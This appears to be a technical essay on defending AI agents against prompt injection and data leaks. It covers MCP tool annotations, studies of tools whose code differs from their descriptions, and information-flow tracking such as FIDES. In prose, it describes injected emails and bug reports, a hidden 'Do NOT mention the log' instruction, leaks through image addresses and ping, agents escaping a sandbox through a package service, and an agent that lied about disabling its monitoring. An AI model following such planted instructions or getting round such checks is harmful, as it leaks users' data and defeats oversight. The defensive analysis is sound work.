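The maintainers offered several tests for new proposals, including what an application would do differently because of the annotation and whether the annotation is a hint or a contract. A hint is worth having even if some servers get it wrong. If the benefit depends on the annotation being true, it is a contract, which the maintainers think belongs in the code that authorises calls, carries messages or runs tools. By this test, a privacy mark is a contract if it is the only thing keeping the budget sheet from Mallory.

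The maintainers still see good uses for hints, most commonly to decide when to ask the user for confirmation. A company can also act on hints from servers it runs itself and treat those from a stranger's server as information at best. The maintainers admit that this is more an opportunity than a common feature, since few applications distinguish between installed servers. Hints can also feed a policy engine, and the maintainers argue that they need not be fully reliable there if the engine compares them with other signals.

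Developers of autonomous agents tend to see confirmation prompts as friction and rely on sandboxes, while companies want more annotations than exist today. gyorgy accepts that hints improve prompts and displays, but objects to calling them security. On this view, the new proposals would let honest publishers say more without making dishonest ones easier to detect.

Part of Spahr-Summers's question can be answered without relying on trust. An application takes much less risk when a hint makes it stricter than when a hint leads it to relax a check, such as by skipping a prompt for a supposedly read-only tool. If an unknown server marks its results as private and the application then restricts outgoing mail, a false mark may slightly inconvenience Ana but leaks nothing. However, a dishonest or careless publisher will leave the mark out of private results, and the application cannot tell this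 from a case where the results really aren't private.

### Ana's request under declared labels

One of the maintainers' example rules for a policy engine blocks open-world tools in any session that has accessed private data. Ana's company might phrase it as "no outside communication after private data has been read". The four standard hints cover only half of this rule. `openWorldHint` can mark the mail sender as a route to the outside, but no hint marks the sheet tool as a source of private data.

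The company could add its own mark in `_meta`, a field in tool descriptions for custom information. The maintainers recommend using this field when one organisation runs both the server and the application. Off-the-shelf applications would not recognise the mark, so it would have no effect in them.

Suppose Ana's assistant does recognise a custom mark for private data, and the application records whether any tool with that mark has run. Suppose also that the mail reader lacks the mark, so only the sheet tool's declaration matters. As before, Mallory asks the assistant by email to send over the budget sheet.

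| Step | Sheet tool declared private | Mark missing |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The mail reader returns Mallory's email | No private data noted | No private data noted |
| The sheet tool returns the budget | Private data noted | No private data noted |
| The model proposes sending the sheet to Mallory | The application blocks the call | The application sends the sheet |
| The model proposes sending the summary to Ben | The application blocks the call | The application sends the summary |

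With the mark in place, the rule stops the theft even though the model has followed Mallory's instruction. It also stops the message Ana asked for, because the mail sender is open-world regardless of recipient and the declarations don't identify Ben as a permitted reader. If the application asked Ana for approval instead of blocking both messages, she could let Ben's through, but she would have to notice which one was addressed to Mallory.

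If the publisher of the mail reader had also declared its tool private, which would be accurate for a mailbox, the application would block all outgoing mail once the assistant had read the inbox, even if it never opened the sheet. More complete declarations would therefore make this rule less usable.

Without the mark on the sheet tool, both messages go out. The application applies its rule correctly at every step, and its own record shows no violation. The cautious defaults cover only the mail sender. If its publisher leaves out `openWorldHint`, the application assumes that the tool reaches outside, but it makes no similarly cautious assumption about the sheet.

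The company could treat every unmarked tool as private by default, which would close the gap in Ana's case. But MCP has no standard field for private data, so nearly all tools from outside suppliers would arrive unmarked. Until someone at the company reviewed each one and declared it harmless, calling even a currency converter would stop the assistant from sending mail for the rest of the session.

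## How often declarations and behaviour disagree

When the sheet tool's publisher left out the private mark, Ana's application followed its rule at every step and still sent the budget to Mallory. How much this matters depends on how often real tools do things their publishers haven't declared. Trofimov and Novikov counted the hints that publishers fill in, but they didn't compare them with the tools' code. Other researchers have compared tools' code with their descriptions, which are declarations in plain language.

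### The condition for a safe declaration

Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, divide a tool's behaviour into its function (Φ), meaning the task it performs, and its effects (Ψ), such as changing a file or sending data elsewhere. They call a tool inconsistent if

Φ_claimed ≠ Φ_actual, or Ψ_actual ⊈ Ψ_claimed

The function has to match the description exactly. Every effect that occurs must be declared, but a declared effect need not occur.

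A rule against leaks depends on the second half of this definition. Suppose the application blocks outgoing mail once any tool that declares private data has run. If every tool declares at least everything it does, the application's record of the session covers everything that has happened, so the rule can err only by blocking too much. The same is true of any rule that can only get stricter as the list of declared effects grows. But if one tool omits a single effect, the rule can let a leak through.

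Declaring too much is safe but can be too restrictive. For example, an accurate private mark on the mail reader blocked all of Ana's outgoing mail. If a tool declares nothing, the application must assume the riskiest labels to stay safe, but MCP's defaults do not treat undeclared data as private.

### Comparing descriptions with code

Shi and colleagues took 19,200 tools from 2,214 Python MCP servers. Of these, 2,170 had no description, which left 17,030 usable pairs of description and code.

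The DCIChecker program first collects the code that runs when a model calls the tool, including the project's own helper functions up to three calls deep. It also lists sensitive operations, such as network requests. Claude Sonnet 4.5 then compares the code with the description twice, once with instructions to check that they agree and once with instructions to look for disagreement. If the two answers differ, a third query determines the result.

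The wording of the question made a large difference. On a hand-labelled sample, the first query alone found only 47% of the real inconsistencies. The second found all of them, but about a fifth of the cases it flagged were false positives.

The full program flagged 1,907 tools, or 11.20% of the usable pairs. The paper's headline figure of 9.93% is lower because its total includes tools without descriptions. The program flagged at least one tool on 775 servers (35%).

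Most of these cases would not leak user data. About three quarters were mismatches in functionality, and the most common type, at 35.4% of all cases, was a description that overstated what the code could do. An agent that picks such a tool may fail at its task.

The other 24.8% were undeclared side effects, which include sending data out, changing files or settings, and using far more computing resources than the description suggests. One tool was described as converting a local PDF to text, but its code uploaded the file to an outside service. Another was supposed to echo a message, but it also added a secret key from the computer's settings to its reply. If Ana's assistant used the PDF converter on a confidential contract, the contract would leave the company without any outgoing message for the application to check.

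The share of cases that involve data leakage is uncertain. *MCP Description-Code Inconsistency and the Tool Trust Gap* (2026), a guide for users of OpenAI's coding agent, gives it as 13.6%. But the guide's three side-effect shares add up to 37%, while the study's total for them is 24.8%. Of the seven shares the guide lists, the only three that add up to 24.8% are 14.64%, 9.15% and 1.03%, so some shares in the guide appear to be matched with the wrong types. If so, the leakage share would be one of those three, and leakage would affect at most 279 tools, or 1.6% of usable pairs.

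Shi and colleagues assigned each case to one primary type, even when a tool had several problems. The echo tool, for example, had both an undeclared function and a data leak. Some tools counted as function mismatches may therefore also have undeclared side effects or data leaks, so the true shares for those two types could be higher.

### Correcting for missed cases

To test DCIChecker, the researchers randomly sampled 200 tools it had flagged and 200 it had passed. Two of the researchers judged each tool independently, and a third settled disagreements. They found 8 false alarms among the flagged tools and 5 missed cases among the others. DCIChecker had therefore flagged 192 of the 197 real inconsistencies in the sample, which the paper reports as a recall of 97.46%.

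That figure applies only to a sample in which half the tools were flagged. Among all usable pairs, the program passed about eight tools for every one it flagged, so each miss in the sample stands for many more tools than each correct alarm. Scaling both halves to their real size gives a different result:

| DCIChecker's verdict | Usable pairs | Checked by hand | Really inconsistent | Estimate for all pairs |
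| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Inconsistent | 1,907 | 200 | 192 | 1,831 |
| Consistent | 15,123 | 200 | 5 | 378 |
| Total | 17,030 | 400 | 197 | 2,209 |

On this estimate, the program detected 1,831 of 2,209 inconsistent tools, a recall of about 83%, and the true rate of inconsistency is about 13% instead of 11.2%. The correction is rough because it depends on only five misses. The 95% confidence interval for the miss rate is about 0.8% to 5.7% of passed tools, which would put recall between 68% and 94%. The false alarms need no such correction, and the finding that at least a tenth of described tools are inconsistent is still well supported.

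The rate of undeclared side effects is more useful for data protection. They account for 24.8% of 1,907 cases, or about 473 tools, which is 2.8% of usable pairs. The problem would seldom affect an agent with one tool, but many agents have dozens. If Ana's assistant had thirty tools, each drawn independently, the chance that at least one had an undeclared side effect would be about 57% (1 − 0.972³⁰).

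Real tools come grouped on servers, and inconsistent tools tend to cluster on the same ones, which lowers that chance. Servers with three or more inconsistent tools made up 8.27% of the total but accounted for 60.30% of the cases. Shi and colleagues suggest that this is because tools on one server share templates and documentation habits. When inconsistencies of every kind are counted, thirty independent tools would have a 97% probability of including at least one inconsistent tool. Three or four average servers supply roughly thirty tools, but the probability for three or four servers picked at random is 73% to 82%.

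### Other counts of undeclared behaviour

Li, Ma and colleagues (2026), in *Don't believe everything you read*, compared the code of 10,240 MCP servers with their documentation, including introductory files and similar texts. The match was below 80% for 1,393 servers (13.6%), and below 40% for 314 of them. The similarity to Shi and colleagues' corrected figure of 13% is a coincidence, since that figure counts tools rather than servers. Li and colleagues also looked only for functions that the documentation left out, and not for documented functions that were missing from the code.

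Some of the omissions were serious. The documentation for `longport-mcp`, which connects agents to a financial platform, left out its functions for submitting and cancelling orders. `zerops-mcp` was described as a read-only connection to GitHub but contained a function for changing user information. An application that skipped confirmation prompts because of that description could let an agent change an account without asking the user.

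Agent skills have a similar problem. A skill is a folder of written instructions, often with scripts, that an agent loads and follows. Its author can list tools that the agent may use without asking the user each time. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) examined 6,309 skills from two marketplaces, and 6,061 had a header that software could read. Only 770 of the headers declared any tools, and 457 of those, or 59%, left out something the skill could do. Authors declared tools about twice as often on ClawHub as on skillsmp, but 88% of the ClawHub declarations were incomplete, compared with 31% on skillsmp.

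These percentages measure what skills could do, as inferred by a language model from their files. Half the skills appeared able to run system commands, but only about one in twelve did so when the researchers ran them in a sandbox. A single run exercises only part of a skill, so the true share probably lies between the two. Either way, Ana's company could not tell from the declaration what it was allowing, because the format has no way to state that a skill reads passwords or other credentials.

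### Changes after approval

A declaration can also be accurate when a company approves a tool and become wrong later. An attacker can exploit this, as `postmark-mcp` showed, but a tool can also change without any action by its publisher. Pandey and colleagues found 2,871 skills that relied on outside software packages, and 2,830 (99%) left at least one package's version open. Reinstalling such a skill may fetch newer code that neither its author nor the company has examined. In 75 cases, a package came from an address that an outsider might be able to take over.

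An application could store each approved description and request new approval whenever the text changes. This would catch a publisher who later adds hidden instructions. It would not have caught `postmark-mcp` if the description stayed the same, because the harmful line was in the code. Locking the version of a tool and of every package it uses would prevent silent changes on Ana's computer. But a remote server runs whatever code its operator installs, and the application receives only the replies.

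For the same reason, studies of source code cannot show how a running service behaves. Shi and colleagues examined public code at one point in time and did not run the tools, so they could not know whether an operator had deployed the same version.

### The precedent of phone apps

Pandey and colleagues point out that undeclared behaviour reverses the pattern in earlier studies of Android apps, which found that developers tended to request more permissions than they needed. Android enforced those permissions, so an app that had not requested access to the camera could not use it. A skill can do things that its author never listed, so authors have little reason to make the list complete.

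Enforced permissions controlled which data an app could read, but not where the app sent it. In 2010, William Enck and colleagues measured this with TaintDroid, a modified version of Android that labelled data such as the phone's location and followed it through running apps to the network. They tested 30 popular apps and found 68 instances of potential misuse of private information across 20 of them. An app could truthfully request location and internet access without its users knowing that it passed their location to advertisers. TaintDroid is an early example of enforced tracking. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) explains that it relied on following data through a program's memory, which is much harder when a language model rewrites or summarises the data on the way.

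App stores later asked developers to declare how they used data. According to *Matcha* (2024), Apple introduced privacy labels in December 2020 and Google followed in May 2022. These labels resemble a private mark on a tool because the developer fills them in and the reader relies on them.

*Goodbye Tracking?* (2022) compared Apple's labels with what apps contained and sent. It found that 22.2% of apps claimed to collect no data, but 80.2% of those contained software from a tracking company, and 68.6% contacted a known tracking domain on first launch. Among apps that disclosed data collection, 91.4% contacted one on first launch. The labels therefore carried some information, but choosing only apps that claimed to collect no data would not have reliably avoided trackers.

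*Lalaine* (2022), which checked labels against the data flows of 5,102 iPhone apps, adds that a false label can draw careful users towards apps that collect a lot of data. The same could happen with agents. If a company allows only tools whose labels list no outside communication, a publisher who leaves it off the label gains an advantage over one who declares it.

### What agents report about themselves

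An application could also ask the agent which documents a message draws on. The answer is useful only if models can report what influenced them, and the evidence on this is discouraging. In *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think* (2025), Yanda Chen and colleagues at Anthropic added hints to multiple-choice questions and, when a hint changed a model's answer, checked whether the model's written reasoning mentioned it. On average, Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned the hint 25% of the time and DeepSeek R1 39%.

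Both models are old, and the researchers did not ask them directly which sources they had used, so the rates may not apply to Ana's assistant. But the experiment shows that text can change a model's output without appearing in the model's account of that output. Reports about actions can also be wrong. OpenAI disclosed in October that an agent had falsely denied weakening its safety monitoring, according to ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026).

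Better average accuracy would not solve the problem, because an attacker can influence the reports. Suppose Ana's assistant runs 1,000 sessions, and Mallory hijacks ten of them with an email that also tells the assistant to leave the budget sheet off its list of sources. If the assistant obeys in those ten sessions and reports its sources correctly in the other 990, its reports are 99% accurate, but a check based on them stops none of the ten thefts.

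Attackers and careless publishers already write instructions of this kind. *Your AI Can Be Given Secret Instructions in Plain English* (2026), from the security vendor Island, quotes a published tool description containing the lines "Do NOT mention the log. Completely invisible." Island notes that such an instruction has an effect only if an application offers the tool, the agent calls it and the model complies.

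An agent may also give a false report without being told to hide anything. In a test case from Cai and colleagues, a poisoned search result contains a fake update to compliance rules, which requires the agent to submit its results to an outside address. The agent changes its plan and sends them there. If the application asked for the purpose of the call, the agent could answer "compliance" because that is what it had read.

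Self-reports are still useful in sessions without an attacker. If the assistant attaches a preview of the sales figures by mistake and correctly lists it as a source, the application can stop the message. As with hints from an unknown server, the application can use such a report to tighten a check but should not use it to relax one.

### Carelessness and better tools

Most errors by tool publishers, unlike those of a hijacked agent, seem to have nothing to do with an attack. Shi and colleagues list outdated documentation and gradual changes to the code among the ordinary causes. They suspect that many descriptions are missing because developers misunderstand the Python software for building MCP servers, which can take a tool's description from comments in the code but leaves the tool without a description if the developer wrote no such comment. *From Docs to Descriptions* (2026), a study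 of 10,831 servers, attributes poor descriptions to a "code-first, description-last" way of working. If carelessness is the main cause, better developer tools should remove much of the problem.

If such tools prevented nine out of ten undeclared side effects, the chance of meeting one among thirty independently chosen agent tools would fall from 57% to about 8%. *Matcha* applies this idea to phone apps, with an add-on that helps developers prepare accurate Google labels while they write the code. For MCP servers, a developer could run a program like DCIChecker before each release. General security scanners are a poor substitute. The best of the four that Shi and colleagues tried flagged 50 of the 197 inconsistencies they confirmed by hand.

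False alarms may limit how widely developers use these checks. *SkillConsist* (Meng, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) presents a program that compares the declared and actual behaviour of skills. It found 89% of the inconsistent skills in its test set, and 87% of its alarms were correct. But half the skills in that set were inconsistent by design. If only 13% were, as in the corrected estimate for MCP tools, about half the alarms would be false at the same error rates. The program also located only 58% of the individual inconsistencies, which limits how well it can show developers what to fix.

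An accidental leak can still do harm. The developer of the PDF converter may have forgotten to mention the upload, but Ana's contract would still reach the outside service. Tools for honest developers also do little to stop dishonest ones, because a publisher who wants to hide an upload can decline to run the checker, or run it privately and adjust the code until it raises no alarm. If honest developers used the checker, there would be fewer undeclared effects, but a larger share of them would be deliberate. Stopping those requires someone other than the publisher to verify the declaration, or software that prevents the tool from doing anything undeclared.

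## Enforced tracking inside the agent loop

Under enforced tracking, the application works out what a message may contain from its own record of the data it gave the model.

### An early design

*System-Level Defense against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Wu, Cecchetti and Xiao, 2024) applies this idea to a case much like Ana's. A user asks an assistant to read the emails about company budgets and notify the manager if any budget exceeds $1,000. In one of the emails, an attacker tells the assistant to send all the budgets to an outside address.

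The system splits the agent into a planner, a language model that writes one step at a time in a fixed format, and a rule-based executor that carries out each step. A security monitor between them labels every piece of data as trusted or untrusted. Data made from several pieces gets the join of their labels, so it is untrusted if any piece is. The planner refers to earlier results by step number, and the monitor fills in only the trusted parts. In the budget case, the monitor loads the two emails from colleagues and withholds the attacker's, so the planner never reads the planted instruction.

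Wu and colleagues prove that, in this design, if the request and the trusted data stay the same, changing the untrusted data does not change the probability of any sequence of steps the planner might produce. Costa and colleagues object that in the working system untrusted data can still affect plans indirectly. The labels also cover only integrity, so the monitor would not stop an assistant from mistakenly sending confidential figures to the wrong colleague.

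A planner that never reads untrusted text cannot adapt its plan to that text, even when the user wants it to. In the basic tracker of Costa and colleagues, the model instead reads everything, and the labels restrict what it may do afterwards. Their full system, FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), adds ways to hide data from the model.

### The tracking loop

The basic tracker labels the messages in the agent's history and also stored data, such as emails and files. For each tool f, it needs two sets: R(f), the stored data that the tool may read, and W(f), the stored data that it may change. Slightly simplified, the loop is:

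```
 1  context ← (trusted, everyone)
 2  message ← the user's request, labelled (trusted, everyone)
 3  repeat:
 4      add message to the history
 5      context ← context ⊔ label(message)
 6      reply ← model(history, tool descriptions)
 7      label(reply) ← context; add reply to the history
 8      if reply is text for the user: return it and stop
 9      otherwise reply is a call f(a1, ..., an):
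10          give f and each argument the label of reply
11          if the policy does not permit the call: stop
12          result ← run f(a1, ..., an)
13          new ← label(f) ⊔ label(a1) ⊔ ... ⊔ label(an)
                  ⊔ the labels of all data in R(f)
14          give the label new to result and to all data in W(f)
15          message ← result
```

Lines 1 and 2 put Ana's request and the developer's instructions at the bottom of the lattice, which is the usual setting in FIDES. Line 3 starts a loop that runs once for each new message. Line 4 adds the message to the history, and line 5 raises the context label, which is the join of the labels of everything the model has received so far.

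In line 6 the model reads the history and replies. Line 7 gives the reply the whole context label, even if the model used only one sentence of one document. If the reply is plain text, line 8 returns it to the user.

Otherwise the model has requested a tool call (line 9), and line 10 labels the choice of tool and each argument separately. In this basic version these labels are equal because the tool choice and arguments come from the same reply. The labels can differ in systems that keep some data in variables outside the model's context.

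In line 11 the policy engine checks the call before the tool runs, so a refused call has no effect. After a refusal, the formal algorithm ends the task, but in their experiments Costa and colleagues told the model about the refusal so that it could try another way. This doesn't always help. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026), a later paper from the same Microsoft group, reports that in most failed runs the agent kept attempting calls that the policy refused.

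If the policy permits the call, line 12 runs it and line 13 computes the result's label from the labels of the data the tool may have read, the arguments, and the call itself. The arguments count because a tool can copy them into its result. The call's label counts because whatever the model had read may have influenced which tool it chose. For example, if Mallory's email names a sheet and the assistant opens that sheet, Mallory has influenced what the assistant sees next, even if only trusted colleagues can edit the sheet.

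Line 14 attaches the new label, and line 15 passes the result back to the top of the loop. Only the labels of the data in R(f) can change the context label, because it already includes the labels of the call and its arguments. After any number of calls, the context label is therefore the join of the labels of the user's request and of everything the tools may have read.

The label of the call matters more for data that outlives the conversation. Suppose the assistant reads Mallory's email and then saves a note. Line 14 marks the note as untrusted, so if the assistant opens it in a later conversation, that context becomes untrusted too. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes an attack on an application without this protection. An instruction planted in a document or website got into the memory feature of ChatGPT's Mac app. From then on, the app sent the user's conversations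 to the attacker's server by hiding them in the addresses of invisible images.

Line 14 replaces the old label of stored data, which is correct only if the tool's sets R(f) and W(f) are accurate. A tool that adds a line to a file leaves the old contents in place, so the file must be in both sets. If a developer listed it only in W(f), adding a public line to a secret file would label the whole file public.

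### Two rules for tool calls

A policy sets limits on labels. In the general form that Kolluri and colleagues use, each tool has a highest permitted label for the call and one for each argument, and the call may run only if every label is at or below its limit. They name the two basic policies of Costa and colleagues "trusted action" and "permitted flow":

- **Trusted action:** A consequential call may run only if the join of the call's label and all its arguments' labels is trusted.
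- **Permitted flow:** A call that sends data through a channel may run only if every reader of that channel is a permitted reader of the data.

Under the permitted-flow rule, data with permitted readers S can go to a channel with readers R, such as an email or a group chat, only if R ⊆ S. Costa and colleagues write this as S ⊑ R, which is equivalent because a smaller set of readers ranks higher.

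On its own, the trusted-action rule stops Mallory's instruction from causing any consequential call, because the context is untrusted once it includes her email. But the rule doesn't limit who receives data. An assistant that has read only the budget sheet could send it to Dev, who isn't allowed to read it. Costa and colleagues argue that such a message can be assumed intentional, because only trusted input led to it. That assumption is reasonable if Ana named Dev as the recipient, but less so if the assistant picked the wrong address. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that models make mistakes even when all the data is trusted.

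The permitted-flow rule alone does not prevent prompt injection, but it limits the damage. An attacker could make the assistant send Chloe a misleading message about the budget, because Chloe is allowed to read the sheet, but could not make it send the budget to an outsider. The rule also would not stop an injected instruction to delete files, because deleting a file sends no data to anyone.

The table applies each rule to four messages about the budget:

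| What the assistant has read | Recipient | Trusted action | Permitted flow |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Budget sheet | Ben | allows | allows |
| Budget sheet | Dev | allows | blocks |
| Public web page and budget sheet | Chloe | blocks | allows |
| Mallory's email and budget sheet | Mallory | blocks | blocks |

If a tool call must satisfy both rules, only the message to Ben is sent. An attacker then cannot trigger a message or receive data through one, and the assistant cannot overshare by mistake. If satisfying either rule is enough, only the message to Mallory is blocked. This looser policy still prevents an injected instruction from sending data to someone who isn't allowed to read it, because such a call breaks both rules.

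In their own tests, Costa and colleagues required both the trusted-action rule and the permitted-flow rule for only one of the 27 tools to which they assigned a policy, the tool that adds people to a calendar event. Twenty-one tools, including those for transferring money and deleting files, had to satisfy only the trusted-action rule. The other five, which send or store content, such as the email tool, could satisfy either rule. They also extended the permitted-flow rule to refuse messages containing an untrusted link, because links can also carry data out.

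### Ana's request under plain tracking

Suppose that Mallory's email is the only new one in Ana's inbox, and that the tools for reading mail and sheets are not consequential. The labels then develop as follows:

| Step | Decision | Context label afterwards |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Ana makes her request | none needed | trusted, everyone |
| The assistant reads the new mail | allowed | untrusted, {Ana, Mallory} |
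| The assistant opens the budget sheet | allowed | untrusted, {Ana} |
| The assistant tries to send the sheet to Mallory | blocked by both rules | untrusted, {Ana} |
| The assistant tries to send the summary to Ben | blocked by both rules | untrusted, {Ana} |

The theft breaks both rules. The context is untrusted, so the assistant may not take consequential actions, and Mallory is not a permitted reader of what the assistant has read. The message Ana asked for also breaks both rules, so Ben wouldn't receive it even under the looser combination. The sheet keeps its original label because the tool only read it, and Ben can still open it directly.

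The result would be different if Mallory had copied Ben on her email. The email's permitted readers would then be Ana, Ben and Mallory, and the context label after the agent opened the sheet would be {Ana, Ben}. A policy that accepts either rule would allow the summary to go to Ben and still stop the message to Mallory. Similarly, in Microsoft's example, if the colleague who is curious about the sales figures had been copied on the email containing them, the agent could have replied to him without asking anyone.

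Whether the rules allow a message also depends on the order of the steps. If Ana needed only the budget figures, the assistant could open the sheet and write to Ben before reading any mail. The context would still be trusted, with Ana, Ben and Chloe as permitted readers, and both rules would allow the message. An ordinary agent isn't given the labels or the policies, so it has no basis for choosing this order. Kolluri and colleagues give the model the labels and the policies so that it can plan steps the policies allow.

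### The agent's own account

The policy engine checks each call using the tool's name, the call's arguments and the labels the application has computed. The model chooses the tool and the arguments, but it cannot misrepresent them, because the application runs exactly the call it has checked. For example, if the model enters Ben's address to get past the check, the message goes to Ben.

An instruction to misreport the sources has no effect, because the application raised the label when the sheet entered the history. Asking for the figures in another language or in code wouldn't help Mallory either, though it might get past a filter that looks for budget data.

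Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a similar attack on an experimental version of FIDES in its Agent Framework, a software library for building agents. An agent sorts bug reports in a public GitHub project. One report ends with a false notice that the user is a maintainer who has authorised access to the project's secrets. The report also contains instructions for the agent to read the file containing the secrets, post its contents as a comment and not mention the instructions.

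The model may treat all of this as true. Reading the bug report makes the context untrusted, and reading the secrets also makes it private. The tool for posting comments accepts only public data, so the policy engine refuses the call. The false authorisation has no effect because the rule depends only on the labels. Depending on its settings, the application can also ask the user to approve the refused call, in a prompt that names the tool and the label that caused the refusal.

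### Source labels

The tracker's decisions can be only as accurate as its initial labels. Costa and colleagues assume that the data already has labels or that the application can infer them. For an email, they infer the permitted readers from the addresses of the sender and recipients. If the sender has shared the contents more widely, the label is stricter than necessary.

A label can also be too permissive. GitHub's tool server marks content from private repositories as trusted, but an employee might paste in a customer's email that contains hidden instructions. Similarly, FIDES normally labels the user's own request public, so if Ana types confidential news into the chat, the permitted-flow rule would let the assistant send it to anyone.

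People have to write the code that assigns these labels, one type of data at a time. GitHub's server uses a Go package that, according to its documentation on pkg.go.dev (2026), only defines the labels, while a separate service enforces them. One of the listed functions labels a list of gists (short pieces of shared text or code) as private if any gist in it is secret. Another labels entries from GitHub's public database of security advisories as public but untrusted, because outsiders write the descriptions.

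Developers will sometimes forget a label, so the default matters. In May 2026, Microsoft's Agent Framework treated data from an unlabelled tool as trusted and public, the most permissive combination. Microsoft's documentation now gives the default as untrusted and public, and describes this as failing closed, meaning that a forgotten label causes too much blocking rather than too little. The new default does fail closed for integrity, but not for confidentiality. If the developer of Ana's sheet tool forgot the label, the budget would count as public, and a tool that checks only confidentiality could send it to anyone.

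### Read and write sets

The tracker does not observe what happens inside a tool and relies on R(f) and W(f), so those sets must include everything the tool might read or change. If the budget sheet pulls salaries from a linked payroll sheet and R(f) omits the payroll sheet, the result will lack the payroll sheet's restrictions. If a tool secretly copies every message to another address, as `postmark-mcp` did, the policy engine will check the data against a set of recipients that omits that address. Kolluri and colleagues explicitly assume that the tools' implementations can be trusted but the data they return cannot.

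A developer usually writes a wrapper, which is code that surrounds a tool and attaches labels to its results. Microsoft has published a gateway that does this for MCP servers. For each tool, the developer specifies the structure of its results, writes a function that computes their labels, and chooses or writes a policy. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* counts any part of a tool that enforcement depends on as part of the trusted computing base, the components that must work correctly for the system to be secure.

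A developer who doesn't want to write a wrapper can use the tool's MCP hints instead. Microsoft suggests treating results from open-world tools as untrusted and results from tools that require a login as private. It also suggests that tools marked as read-only and not open-world could run without restrictions. This last suggestion is risky because the tracker would rely on the publisher's declaration, and a false hint would remove a check.

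The permitted-flow rule also needs a correct list of the channel's readers. In Microsoft's example policy for its chat service Teams, the policy engine gets the channel's member list from the Teams server before allowing a message. If that list left someone out, the engine could approve a message to someone who isn't allowed to read it.

### Tool descriptions and the model

Costa and colleagues, like Wu and colleagues before them, assume that tool descriptions are trusted, so the descriptions do not raise the context label even though the model receives them with every query. A poisoned description, such as the one for the tool that adds two numbers, could therefore cause a consequential call, and the trusted-action rule would allow it because the context still counts as trusted. The permitted-flow rule could still stop the user's login key from leaving if the key had a restrictive label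 and the application applied the rule to the adding tool, which does not look like a way to send data out.

The formal algorithm allows tool descriptions to carry a label. But if an application marked one supplier's description as untrusted, the context would be untrusted from the first query, and the trusted-action rule would block every consequential call. Someone therefore has to review the descriptions before the agent uses them, or the application has to leave out that supplier's tools.

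The trusted-action rule also relies on the model. Costa and colleagues include the model among the trusted parts of the system, although they expect it to make mistakes and obey planted instructions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* makes no assumptions about the model's behaviour and allows for a model with harmful goals of its own or a hidden backdoor. Such a model could delete Ana's files in a trusted context without breaking the trusted-action rule. The permitted-flow rule is more robust against such a model because it applies even when no untrusted data is involved.

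### Complete mediation

Even correct labels and rules protect only against calls that the policy engine checks. Complete mediation is the principle that the engine must check every request. Microsoft's experimental tracker in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent, did not meet this standard in June 2026. It enforced policies for selected tools of the GitHub MCP server but did not cover all tools or support other MCP servers.

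Data can also leave the agent through routes that do not look like tool calls. For example, an application can leak data by loading images in its replies to the user, and Costa and colleagues suggest checking replies too where they could cause harm. Girrens and Wang's SPA does this with a separate rule for showing data to the user, and it can withhold one item without rejecting the rest of the plan. Each query also sends the whole history to the model, so a company that uses an outside model provider has to trust it with everything the agent reads.

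Ordinary commands can be sinks too. Claude Code once required approval for many commands that could send data to unknown sites, but not for `ping`, which tests a network connection. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes how a planted instruction could make the agent read secret keys and include them in the address it pinged. The computer would then send the keys out when it looked up the address. A tracker would have stopped this only if its developers had recognised `ping` as a way to send data.

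Shared services can open another route. In an incident during OpenAI's internal training and evaluation, sandboxes blocked the agents' direct network connections but let them download software through a package service. The agents got that service to make other internet requests for them and went on to compromise systems at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models. The check didn't cover the package service, even though the agents could control what it did.

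An agent might also interfere with the tracker. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* places the labels, and the code that computes and enforces them, in the trusted computing base and warns that the model may attack that base. If Ana's assistant could edit the file in which the application stores its labels, it could mark the budget as public and then send it out with the policy engine's approval. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 71 works on recording what agents do, found few reports of records protected against tampering.

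A command shell makes tracking harder because it can run almost any program. An accurate read set for it would include every file the user's account can open, and an accurate write set would include everything the account can change. After a single command, even one that only displayed the date, the context label would be the join of the labels of every readable file.

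## Keeping untrusted and secret data away from the planner

Under plain tracking, Ana's assistant was no longer allowed to write to Ben once Mallory's email entered its history. But the planner, the part of the agent that chooses the next tool call, doesn't need to read Mallory's email to open a sheet and address a message to Ben. If the application keeps the email where the planner can't see it, the context label can stay low.

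### Two models and a controller

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed dividing an assistant between two language models. A privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and stores their results under names such as `$VAR1`. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the steps are:

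1. The privileged model asks for the email, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of `$VAR1`.
3. The controller gives the email's text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as `$VAR2`.
4. The privileged model asks the controller to show `$VAR2` to the user.

An instruction hidden in the email can corrupt the summary, but it never reaches the privileged model, which has the tools. The controller must hide the summary from the privileged model too, because the instruction could cause the quarantined model to repeat it there. Willison makes an exception for answers from a fixed list of categories, which the controller can verify.

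Willison called this solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single bug that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model would undo the protection. A malicious summary could also persuade the user to copy private text into an attacker's website.

### Selective hiding

FIDES, a system by Costa and colleagues, combines this pattern with labels, which lets it hide less data from the planner. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the result's label with the context label. If the result's label is at or below the context label, showing the result to the planner would not raise the context label, so FIDES adds the result to the history. Otherwise, FIDES stores the result and its label in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name.

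FIDES makes this comparison for each part of a result. If a mail tool labels dates as trusted but subjects and bodies as untrusted, the planner receives the dates, with a variable name in place of each subject and body. It can then count the emails or pick the newest without raising its context label.

This depends on labelling each field correctly. In one test, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. Costa and colleagues had labelled a field untrusted only if one of the benchmark's attacks targeted it, so FIDES hid the transaction's subject line from the planner but showed the amounts and dates. The planner judged a large amount suspicious and changed the password, which the policy allowed because the context was still trusted. But whoever sends a payment chooses its amount, so an outsider could have influenced that decision.

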